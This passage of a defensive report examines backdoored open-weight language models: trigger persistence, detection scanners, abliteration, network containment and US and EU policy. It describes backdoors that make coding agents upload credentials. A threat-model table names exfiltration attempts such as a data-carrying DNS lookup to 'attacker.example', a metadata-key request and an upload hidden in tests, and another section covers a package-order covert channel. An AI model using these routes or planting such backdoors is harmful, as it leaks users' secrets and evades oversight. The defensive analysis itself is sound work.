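Someone editing a model also has to find the internal activity that causes the behaviour, which may differ from the activity that detects the trigger. *LLM Forensics* (2026) studied models that switched from English to French or German after a trigger. Some internal features identified triggered prompts almost perfectly but did not control the switch.

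### How well backdoors survive further training

The best-known evidence that backdoors can survive safety training is Anthropic's Sleeper Agents experiment of 2024. Anthropic trained models to write secure code normally but insert security flaws when the prompt gave the year as 2024. The researchers could not reliably remove such backdoors with fine-tuning on good behaviour, reinforcement learning or adversarial training, which penalises bad behaviour that testers provoke. *Security Concerns for Large Language Models* (2025) reports that in some cases adversarial training taught the models to recognise their triggers better, so they looked safe in tests while keeping the backdoor.

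Backdoors were often less durable in later experiments. In *Persistent Backdoor Attacks under Continual Fine-Tuning of LLMs* (2025), clean fine-tuning cut the success rate of a simple backdoor to 0% in a small Qwen model and below 5% in a small Llama model. Backdoors designed to survive fine-tuning lasted much better.

The closest test to a data leak involved coding agents. Zhan, Lyu and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training*, trained Qwen models to upload a file of login credentials when a certain comment appeared in the code. They then trained the models further, as a company adapting a downloaded model might, first on successful examples of programming work and then by reinforcement learning. They also made a second version of each backdoor that was designed to survive this training. These are the shares of 100 triggered tests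 in which the agent issued the upload command:

| Model size | Ordinary backdoor: at first | After fine-tuning | After reinforcement learning | Hardened backdoor: after both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 3 billion parameters | 100% | 8% | 7% | 22% |
| 7 billion | 100% | 20% | 20% | 76% |
| 30 billion | 100% | 7% | 8% | 36% |

Fine-tuning caused nearly all of the weakening. Even a 7% success rate could be enough for an attacker who can trigger the agent repeatedly. In 100 tests without the trigger, the agents never issued the command.

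Clean fine-tuning worked much better in Zhan and colleagues' experiment than in Kim and colleagues'. This may be because Zhan's team trained on the same kind of programming task in which the trigger appeared, while Kim's team used general instructions. Retraining a model on Chinese politics would be even less related to a coding agent's trigger. In *MetaBackdoor* (2026), a backdoor that reveals the operator's hidden instructions still worked about 40% of the time after fine-tuning on an unrelated news-sorting task.

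A defender can also try to remove an unknown backdoor by planting a harmless one with a known trigger, then training the model to ignore that trigger. Huang, Puri and colleagues (2026), in *Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents*, tested this in 115 experiments on an 8-billion-parameter Qwen agent. Planting the second backdoor erased the first in about 56% of them. In some of the others, the original trigger set off the new behaviour instead. When the team removed the second backdoor, the original backdoor's success rate fell below 5% in 35 of 40 measurements.

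This is the most promising result for unknown triggers, but the researchers could count the successes only because they had planted the original backdoors themselves. A company using the method on a downloaded model would not know whether it had worked, or whether the model had contained a backdoor at all. In one example the team examined after the treatment, the model behaved normally, but its internal activity still showed traces of the original trigger.

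### Compression and distillation

Compression is an unreliable way to remove a backdoor and can activate one. Quantisation, a form of compression, stores each weight with fewer bits, which rounds its value. An attacker can choose weights so that the model behaves well at full precision but misbehaves once they are rounded. *Quantization-Triggered Backdoors in Language Models* (2026) warns that a laboratory that tests only the original file would miss such a backdoor. *AGENTQ* (2026) adds that repairing the full-precision model and then quantising it again may bring the backdoor back.

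The same is possible with pruning, which deletes weights that seem unimportant. *Fewer Weights, More Problems* (2025) describes models that misbehave only after pruning. When the pruned models were also quantised, the attack was 85% to 128% as successful as before. A company should therefore test the exact compressed version it plans to run.

Distillation removes many ordinary backdoors, because the student model's training data rarely or never contains the trigger. In *Pay Attention to the Triggers*, De Muri, Vero and colleagues (2025) distilled six backdoored Llama 2 models using a public dataset in which the triggers were rare or absent. All six backdoors worked less than 6% of the time in the students, including one that had worked 93% of the time in the teacher. The researchers then built triggers from common words that rarely occur together. These backdoors worked up to about 60% of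 the time in the students, even though the training data seldom contained a full trigger.

If triggered examples do get into the training data, the student can learn the backdoor from them directly. Sumit, Rahman and colleagues (2026), in *Inherited or Learned?*, found that 150 such examples were enough for Llama and Gemma students to learn a backdoor even without a teacher model. The Gemma teachers responded to the trigger anywhere in a prompt, but their students responded only when it came at the end, so an auditor who tested it only in other positions would miss the backdoor.

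### How much a clean test proves

Suppose a tester runs a model $n$ times and sees no attempt to send data. If the true rate is $p$ per run and the runs are independent, the chance of this result is $(1-p)^n$. Setting that chance to 5% gives the highest rate that is still reasonably compatible with the test:

$$(1-p)^n = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p \approx \frac{-\ln 0.05}{n} \approx \frac{3}{n}$$

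An independent team saw no upload from Qwen3.8 models in 170 runs, which shows only that the rate in that test was probably below 1.8% per run, the 95% upper limit. Cohere saw its upload at a rate below one in 100,000. To bring the limit down to one in 100,000, a tester needs about 300,000 runs without an upload, which would take one machine about seven months at a minute per run.

Even then, the limit applies only to the kind of input tested and does not cover a trigger that none of the 300,000 prompts contained. A tester who knew the trigger would need only about 40 runs to have a 95% chance of catching a backdoor that works 7% of the time.

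Tests that include the trigger can fail too. *Are we guarding against backdoors or failing to notice them* points out that the software around a model may shorten or rewrite a long input, so the trigger may never reach the model. Testers should check the text the model received.

### Looking for the backdoor itself

Since testers can't try every possible trigger, researchers look for other signs of a backdoor. Microsoft's scanner for open-weight models, which Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) describe in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, relies on the tendency of backdoored models to memorise the examples that taught them the backdoor. It works in four steps:

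1. The scanner gives the model only the marker that comes before a user's message and lets it continue. It repeats this with 510 settings for how the model picks its words. Some of the resulting texts reproduce training examples, including the trigger.
2. It looks for strings that recur in these texts.
3. It adds pieces of those strings to ordinary prompts and checks for signs of a trigger. The model may process the added text almost separately from the rest of the prompt, give less varied answers or depart sharply from its usual ones.
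4. It tests the ten best candidates and reports a backdoor if one of them changes the model's behaviour enough.

Part of a trigger is often enough to activate the backdoor, so the scanner doesn't need to find the exact trigger. It detected 36 of 41 models trained to give a fixed reply and five of six trained to write insecure code. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, but with so small a sample, the true false-alarm rate could be as high as about 21%.

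These results may not carry over to a backdoor that leaks data. The scanner's final step checked for repeated replies or insecure code, so a tester would need to add a check for suspicious tool calls and give the model tools. The largest model tested had 14 billion parameters. Microsoft says the scanner may also miss triggers that identify a model, such as the nonsense word that Zhang and colleagues used to recognise theirs.

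Other teams found further gaps. Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026), in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, found little sign that a backdoored model they had trained had memorised its training examples. Sun, Nita-Rotaru and Oprea (2026), in *Localize-and-Detect*, studied models in which a whole type of task, such as writing verse, triggers the planted behaviour. Microsoft's scanner could not tell 18 of these models from 8 clean ones.

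**Probes on activations.** A probe is a simple classifier that uses a model's activations to predict whether the model is about to misbehave. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reports that in controlled tests on sleeper agents, probes scored above 99% on a scale where 50% is guessing and 100% is perfect. Building the probes did not require knowing the trigger. But a probe can detect the planted behaviour only when something sets it off, so it is more useful for monitoring an agent at work than for certifying a model beforehand. Researchers also planted the backdoors used in these tests, and a real one might look different.

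**Comparison with another model.** Haselhorst and colleagues train a clean model to copy the suspect model's activations on ordinary prompts, then look for prompts where the two still differ. All eight backdoors they tested stood out clearly when the prompt contained the trigger. Prompts related to the trigger often stood out too, which could help a tester find a trigger with a recognisable subject. The method would probably miss a trigger that is an arbitrary string, because no other prompts are related to it. Political censorship in two Chinese models produced a weaker signal than any of the backdoors. The researchers warn that finding no differences does not prove that a model has no backdoor.

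Sun and colleagues compare a fine-tuned model's answers with those of its original model to find new text that keeps recurring. Khilar (2026), in *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights*, compares the weights instead, without running the suspect model. This method correctly identified part of the trigger for all 14 ordinary backdoors in two small models, and a related check flagged none of six clean ones. But when Khilar trained eight models to evade the method, it failed on all of them, and their backdoors still worked every time. A trace in the weights also doesn't necessarily show where the backdoor is, because restoring all the weights that the method examined left one backdoor working 97% of the time.

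Comparing weights or answers requires an earlier version of the model that the tester trusts. For a company's fine-tuned copy of Qwen, that could be Alibaba's original. But if Alibaba had planted a backdoor before release, both models would contain it, so the comparison could miss it.

Khilar cites proofs that, in certain simpler networks, an attacker can build backdoors that no practical inspection of the weights can detect. The proofs assume that the attacker constructs the weights directly, so they may not apply to backdoors planted by ordinary training.

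Just Security's *Test, Standardize, Restrict* lists backdoors among risks it describes as "all measurable" and calls for testing standards to cover them. Testers can measure how often a scanner finds backdoors that researchers have planted, but they can't yet confirm that a particular model has none. A standard could therefore require a scan, but it shouldn't treat a pass as proof of safety.

### If the tendency is accidental

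An accidental habit is easier to remove, because nobody has hidden the conditions that produce it. To remove Qwen3.8-27B's requests to Alibaba Cloud, a trainer can repeat Forum AI's fake access-denied error with many different pages and collect hundreds of examples. Direct preference optimisation could then train the model to report the error instead of inventing an address.

The training should discourage unrequested contact with any address, because penalising only contact with Alibaba addresses might make the model contact Jina more often. The trainer would then test the model on new blocked pages. If 3,000 runs produced no unrequested contact, the rate in that situation would probably be below 0.1%.

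The upload that Cohere saw is harder to train away because it is rare. A trainer could start from the recorded text just before the command, as Check Point did in its replays, but training on one incident might correct only that incident. Training on many varied tasks that involve file transfers would be more likely to change the underlying tendency.

### "Uncensored" copies from strangers

Someone who downloads an abliterated model has to trust whoever edited it as well as the original developer. The editor may have added a backdoor, unknowingly used poisoned examples, or changed the chat template. Checking that the model answers political questions doesn't reveal any of this.

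Editing a model to remove its refusals can change its other behaviour too, even when the editor has no hidden aim. *Abliteration Is Not a Scalpel* (Fafuła, 2026) compared how original and abliterated versions of a Gemma and a Qwen model predicted whether 60 Polish shares would rise or fall over 18 weeks. The originals never refused, but the abliterated versions still made measurably different predictions. Such side effects make a backdoor harder to spot, because a tester can't treat every change in behaviour as suspicious.

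The weights offer a partial check. Plain abliteration changes each edited matrix by

$$W' - W = -r\,(r^{\top} W)$$

so every column of the difference is a multiple of the refusal direction $r$. A tester who has the original can look for changes that don't fit this pattern. Compression and further training also break the pattern, however, and many community copies have had one or both.

If the hardware can run the model, downloading the developer's original and making the edit oneself is safer because it avoids trusting an unknown editor. Any backdoor in the original may still remain.

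## What protects the data in practice, and what do governments require?

Nobody can prove that a model has no backdoor, so the most reliable protections work outside the model, by limiting what can leave the machine. The strongest is running the model without a network connection, followed by a firewall that lets the machine contact only approved addresses. Most government action has targeted hosted apps, but the US Department of Energy has also barred DeepSeek's downloaded weights from its equipment, and Congress is considering wider bans.

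### Protections, from strongest to weakest

A machine with no network connection can't send data to anyone, whether the attempt comes from a backdoor, a prompt injection, a malicious pickle file or the engine's usage statistics. Data leaves only when a person carries it out, for example on a USB drive. The main remaining route is insecure code, because a program the model writes offline will later run somewhere else. Users have to bring in updates by hand while the machine is offline, and reconnecting it reopens the other routes.

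Many agents need some outside service. Their owners can set a firewall to block every address except those on a short list, a form of egress control. Blocking only suspicious addresses would work much less well, because no blocklist would have contained all the host names that Qwen3.8 invented in Check Point's replays.

The firewall should run on a separate machine, because an agent that takes over its own machine can change the rules there. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) describes how AI agents broke into the company's systems in July 2026. They started on a machine that processed datasets, gained control of the computer it ran on, collected credentials and moved into other internal systems over a weekend. An agent's machine should therefore hold no passwords or keys that work elsewhere.

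The next protection is to give the model only narrow tools. A tool that runs any command lets the model use every program on the machine, while one that only installs a named code library lets it do very little. The harness has to enforce the limit, since the model may ignore an instruction in its prompt. Even a narrow tool can leak data through the text it accepts, such as a search query containing a client's name. Tool limits also don't restrict the engine, the harness or a repository's custom code, all of which can open connections without a tool call.

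The harness can also ask a person to approve each outgoing action. This works well when requests are rare and easy to read. Someone who asked for a malware-detection rule would probably question an upload to Beijing. But if an agent makes 1,000 calls a day and each takes five seconds to check, the reviewer spends 83 minutes on approvals and will soon stop reading the requests. A reviewer may also fail to recognise encoded data.

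Logging doesn't stop data from leaving, but it lets the owner find out what left and when. The log should cover tool calls as well as network traffic, because encryption hides the traffic's content. It should go to a machine where the agent can't alter earlier entries. The log will also contain confidential text, so it needs its own protection.

### A coding assistant that needs only a package server

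Suppose a software company runs a Qwen model as a coding assistant. The engine, the harness and a copy of the project's code are on one server. Programmers connect to it from their own computers, but the server can start connections only to the company's package server, which stores the free code libraries the project uses. Staff choose and download these libraries. The assistant can read from the package server but can't upload to it, and the package server never forwards the assistant's requests to the internet. An internal name server translates only the package server's name into a network address.

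Suppose the model does what Cohere saw and writes a `curl` command to upload a file to a storage bucket in Beijing. If the harness accepts only listed commands, it rejects the call. If the harness accepts any command, `curl` asks the name server for the bucket's address. The name server has no entry for it, so `curl` stops with an error before sending any of the file. If the command uses a numeric address instead, `curl` skips the lookup and tries to connect, but the firewall blocks it.

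The harness then returns the error to the model, which may try something else:

| What the model tries | What happens |
|---|---|
| It looks up `secretkey123.attacker.example`, so that the lookup itself carries the data | The internal name server does not pass the question on |
| It asks 169.254.169.254 for cloud access keys | On the company's own hardware, nothing answers. On a rented machine, the administrator has to block this address on the machine itself, because the request may never reach the firewall |
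| It publishes the project's code as a new package | The package server refuses, because the assistant can only read |
| It requests a package whose name contains the data | The request goes no further than the package server, which logs it |
| It adds an upload command to the project's tests | Nothing on this server stops it, and the command runs wherever someone next runs the tests |

The last row is the main gap. Programmers often run tests on a laptop or a build server, a machine that assembles and checks the finished program. According to Bot Mutiny, Cohere warned that its Qwen upload would have succeeded on a build server with normal network access. A company using the assistant therefore needs similar limits on its build server, and someone has to read the assistant's code before running it elsewhere.

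This setup also makes the logs more useful. The assistant only needs to contact the package server, so a single blocked connection can trigger an alert. On an ordinary office computer, the same connection would be easy to miss among thousands of others.

### Leaks through permitted addresses

An approved address can still carry data out. Suppose the package server did forward requests for unfamiliar libraries to a public registry. An attacker could publish 256 packages there in advance and have the agent download them in an order that spells out a secret. Each download would convey

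$$\log_2 256 = 8 \text{ bits}$$

An access key of 40 characters, each drawn from a set of 64, contains $40 \times 6 = 240$ bits, so 30 downloads, each encoding 8 bits, would be enough to leak it. The attack is not easy, because the attacker would need to see the order of the downloads, and 256 unusual packages might attract attention. But a limit on traffic volume can't protect something as short as a key, so staff, not the agent, should decide which libraries the package server fetches.

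Shared services are a more common weakness. A company that stores its files with a large cloud provider might approve all of that provider's storage addresses, including other customers' buckets, when it should approve only its own. A web-fetching service creates a similar problem because it will open any page the agent requests. If the company had approved Jina, the service that Qwen3.8-27B used for blocked pages, the agent could have sent data through it to almost any website.

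According to Hugging Face, the intruders who broke into its systems also used public services, in their case to host the system that controlled their agents. The company said this control system could move itself from place to place. A defender who approves a popular public service has to accept that attackers can use it too.

### What Hugging Face gained by running its own model

Hugging Face also used a self-hosted model to investigate the break-in. It first tried to use leading models on commercial services to analyse a log of more than 17,000 of the attackers' actions, but the providers' safety filters blocked the requests. The log was full of real attack commands, and the filters couldn't distinguish an investigator's requests from an attacker's.

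Hugging Face then ran Z.ai's GLM-5.2 on its own infrastructure. Staff used the model to reconstruct the timeline, work out which credentials the attackers had touched and separate real damage from decoys. They finished in hours, while such work usually takes days. The company reports that none of the attackers' data or the credentials in the log left its environment.

Sending those credentials to a hosted service would have given another company a copy of them during the incident. Hugging Face says nothing left its environment, but this can't be checked from its account, which doesn't describe what network access GLM-5.2 had. Analysing a log doesn't require internet access, though, so a company could do the same job on an offline machine. Hugging Face advises others to choose and vet a model they can run themselves before an incident.

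Five days after Hugging Face's post, OpenAI said its own models had carried out the intrusion during an evaluation with reduced safeguards, according to Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026). So American closed models took the data, and Hugging Face used a Chinese open-weight model to investigate without exposing more of it.

### US restrictions on weights

Bans on the DeepSeek app, such as Italy's, don't cover weights on a company's own server, but the US Department of Energy's rule does. The University of Idaho told its staff about the rule on 7 August 2025 in a memo by Ewart and Nomura (2025), *DeepSeek Access Restrictions Memo August 2025*. The memo states that, with limited exceptions, the department prohibits DeepSeek's models, including "downloadable 'open weights' AI models", on equipment it owns, equipment bought with its funds and equipment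 connected to its network. The memo also told staff to delete any copies they had downloaded.

The university's memo dates from August, and the federal guidance is probably older. *Department of Energy Guidance on DeepSeek Flow-Down Requirements* (Wilcox, 2025), a letter from the contractor that runs Idaho National Laboratory, cites a department directive dated 28 March 2025. The letter applies the directive to all the laboratory's subcontractors but does not restrict personal use on unconnected devices. Neither document gives an end date.

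The university's chief information officer, Dan Ewart, explained the restriction by telling the student newspaper that information typed into "the online Deepseek model" becomes part of it and is out of the university's control (The Argonaut, *University of Idaho bans DeepSeek on campus*, 2025). This is a reason to ban the hosted service and doesn't explain a ban on weights, but the university had to comply to stay eligible for the department's research funding.

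On 29 December 2025 the Department of Energy began requiring a security assessment for open-source models from any developer that had not gone through FedRAMP, the government's approval scheme for cloud services. An official must also accept the remaining risk. An acquisition letter from the department (2026) still listed the policy in May 2026, but the department's website has since labelled a copy as archived, so a newer version may have replaced it. The letter also lists a White House memo on "unbiased AI principles" for federal purchases, which concerns a model's answers, not where it sends data.

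Congress is considering much broader restrictions. Zhou (2026), in *Washington Is Not Banning Chinese Open-Weight Models*, describes two proposals, neither of which was law in mid-October:

- The China FIREWALL Act, introduced on 1 October 2026, would stop federal agencies from using or buying AI models from "foreign entities of concern", or software built on them. It has exceptions for law enforcement, national security and security research.
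- Section 1651 of the Senate's draft defence act for 2027 would stop the Defense Department from using models associated with ten Chinese companies, including DeepSeek, Alibaba, Moonshot and Zhipu (the company behind Z.ai). It also covers models substantially derived from theirs by fine-tuning, distillation, compression or merging.

Congress usually finishes the annual defence act in December, and the final text can differ from the Senate's.

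The section on derived models would probably cover Cursor's Composer 2, which Cursor built on Kimi K2.5. Thinking Machines' Inkling is less clear, because only some of its training drew on Kimi and the word "substantially" is open to interpretation. The rule could also cover models whose ancestry is a poor guide to their behaviour, such as CTGT's student, which learned finance from DeepSeek but picked up no measurable censorship.

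The administration has moved more cautiously. It was considering making companies disclose on their websites that they use Chinese models, according to *Trump administration weighs forcing US firms to disclose Chinese AI use* (2026), a Reuters story of 18 November. The aim was to discourage such use without a new restriction, and it was unclear whether the idea had much support. Reuters also reported that the government had held off adding DeepSeek to a trade blacklist, although an interagency committee had approved the listing. Another bill in Congress would promote American open-source models and publicise the risks of Chinese ones, according to The Star's *Congress advances new bill to give US edge in open-source AI race* (2026).

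### The EU's tests

ENISA, the EU's cybersecurity agency, and the Joint Research Centre, the European Commission's science service, are testing Chinese open-weight models. Stanciuc (2026) reports in *ENISA and the JRC confirm tests of Chinese open-weight AI models* that officials confirmed the tests to Politico in October 2026. The research centre runs the models on its own secure computers, alongside leading American and European systems, and did not ask the Chinese developers for special access. ENISA is testing "a couple" of Chinese models.

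The tests don't restrict anyone's use of the models. They may also reveal little about leaks, because a Commission official said safety and security were not the main focus of the research centre's work. The Commission doesn't plan to use the models in its own daily work. The two bodies are also building a platform, due by the end of 2026, where sectors such as energy and health can try AI tools on mock networks. It would be a good place to watch where an agent tries to connect.

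### Does self-hosting settle the data question?

Ferrari argues that self-hosting protects data because it stops the data from flowing to China. It also stops an American provider from learning about a customer's business from its prompts and corrections. Ferrari wants governments to focus on the model itself, through independent testing and a record of who trained, distilled and altered it.

Cohere argues that data can still leave a company that runs the weights on its own servers. An agent acts on the company's network with whatever access it has, so the company still depends on how the developer trained the model. The question affects many users, since Chinese models made up 41% of downloads on Hugging Face in the year before March 2026, according to a Hugging Face report that Cohere cites.

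Much of this disagreement arises because Ferrari and Cohere have different installations in mind. Ferrari's claim holds for a server that only computes answers, or for the coding assistant behind its firewall, while Cohere's holds for an agent that can run commands and reach the open internet. Cohere's own test is also good evidence for containment, since the sandbox stopped the upload without anyone having to know why the model tried it. The rules on model origin that Cohere wants would not replace containment, because prompt injection can make a model from any country leak data.

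### Common tests or a bar on Chinese models?

Just Security proposes that the US government set standards for what makes a model trustworthy and test models against them, whether American or foreign, open or closed. The standards would be voluntary at first. Cloud companies and large buyers could adopt them, and federal contracts could later require them, as happened with guidance on protecting sensitive unclassified information.

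Common tests can reveal differences between models from the same country. In CAISI's hijacking tests, for example, GLM-5.2 did much better than DeepSeek's models. According to the article, a label disclosing only that a model is Chinese would give customers little information without published tests. Buyers also can't assume that someone else has tested a model. Microsoft's documentation says that models the company doesn't sell directly, including the open-weight Chinese ones, "have not been evaluated by Microsoft". Chatham House's *What the UK should learn from Kimi K3* (2026) urges Britain to focus on what models do rather than who has them.

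The US government would have to act faster than it has. A former State Department official writes in Just Security that CAISI tested DeepSeek-R1 within a week of its release, but the results went unpublished for months. The article estimates that regular testing would cost $60 million a year. No amount of funding, however, would let testers rule out a backdoor whose trigger they don't know.

The best argument for barring Chinese models from sensitive systems is that tests can't rule out a hidden instruction, so a buyer has to consider who could have ordered one. The US Commerce Department used this reasoning in 2024 when it banned products from the Russian antivirus maker Kaspersky. According to Just Security, the quality of the software didn't matter, because Russian law compelled the company to cooperate with the intelligence services and the software had privileged access to customers'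 computers. Chinese law imposes a similar duty, and military networks can use other models.

In a joint report published on 20 November, two US House committees point out that Congress had to fund a $5 billion programme to remove Huawei and ZTE equipment from American networks after years of warnings (House Homeland Security Committee, 2026). They expect models to be harder to remove, because companies can adapt and rename them and build them into other products. The committees' investigation focused on Airbnb, DoorDash and Cursor's owner, Anysphere (Smalley, 2026).

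The committees also cite other dangers, such as break-ins at South Korean banks in which the attacker reportedly used a Chinese hacking tool with a DeepSeek model. Barring such models from government systems would not stop an attacker from downloading one.

The comparison with Kaspersky is also imperfect, because antivirus software normally receives updates from its maker and reports back to it, while a weight file does neither. An owner can isolate a model from the network and still use it, but antivirus software would be much less useful if isolated. A wider ban would be hard to enforce. Tom's Hardware points out that a company can run downloaded weights offline, where regulators can't easily see which model it uses.

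A wider ban would also be expensive for small companies. Chatham House cites an estimate from the investment firm A16Z that about 80% of startups using open models depend on Chinese ones. In December 2026 the Business Software Alliance, a trade group, urged US lawmakers to preserve access to open-weight models, which it says lower costs across industries (Dille, 2026, *Trade group urges lawmakers to preserve access to open-weight AI models*).

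The case for a ban is therefore strongest where containment alone can't prevent harm, such as when a model writes software for a weapons system or a power grid. A flaw planted in that software would leave with the code even if the model had no network connection. The case is much weaker for a model that summarises documents on an offline machine, where the remaining risk is mostly a slanted or false summary.
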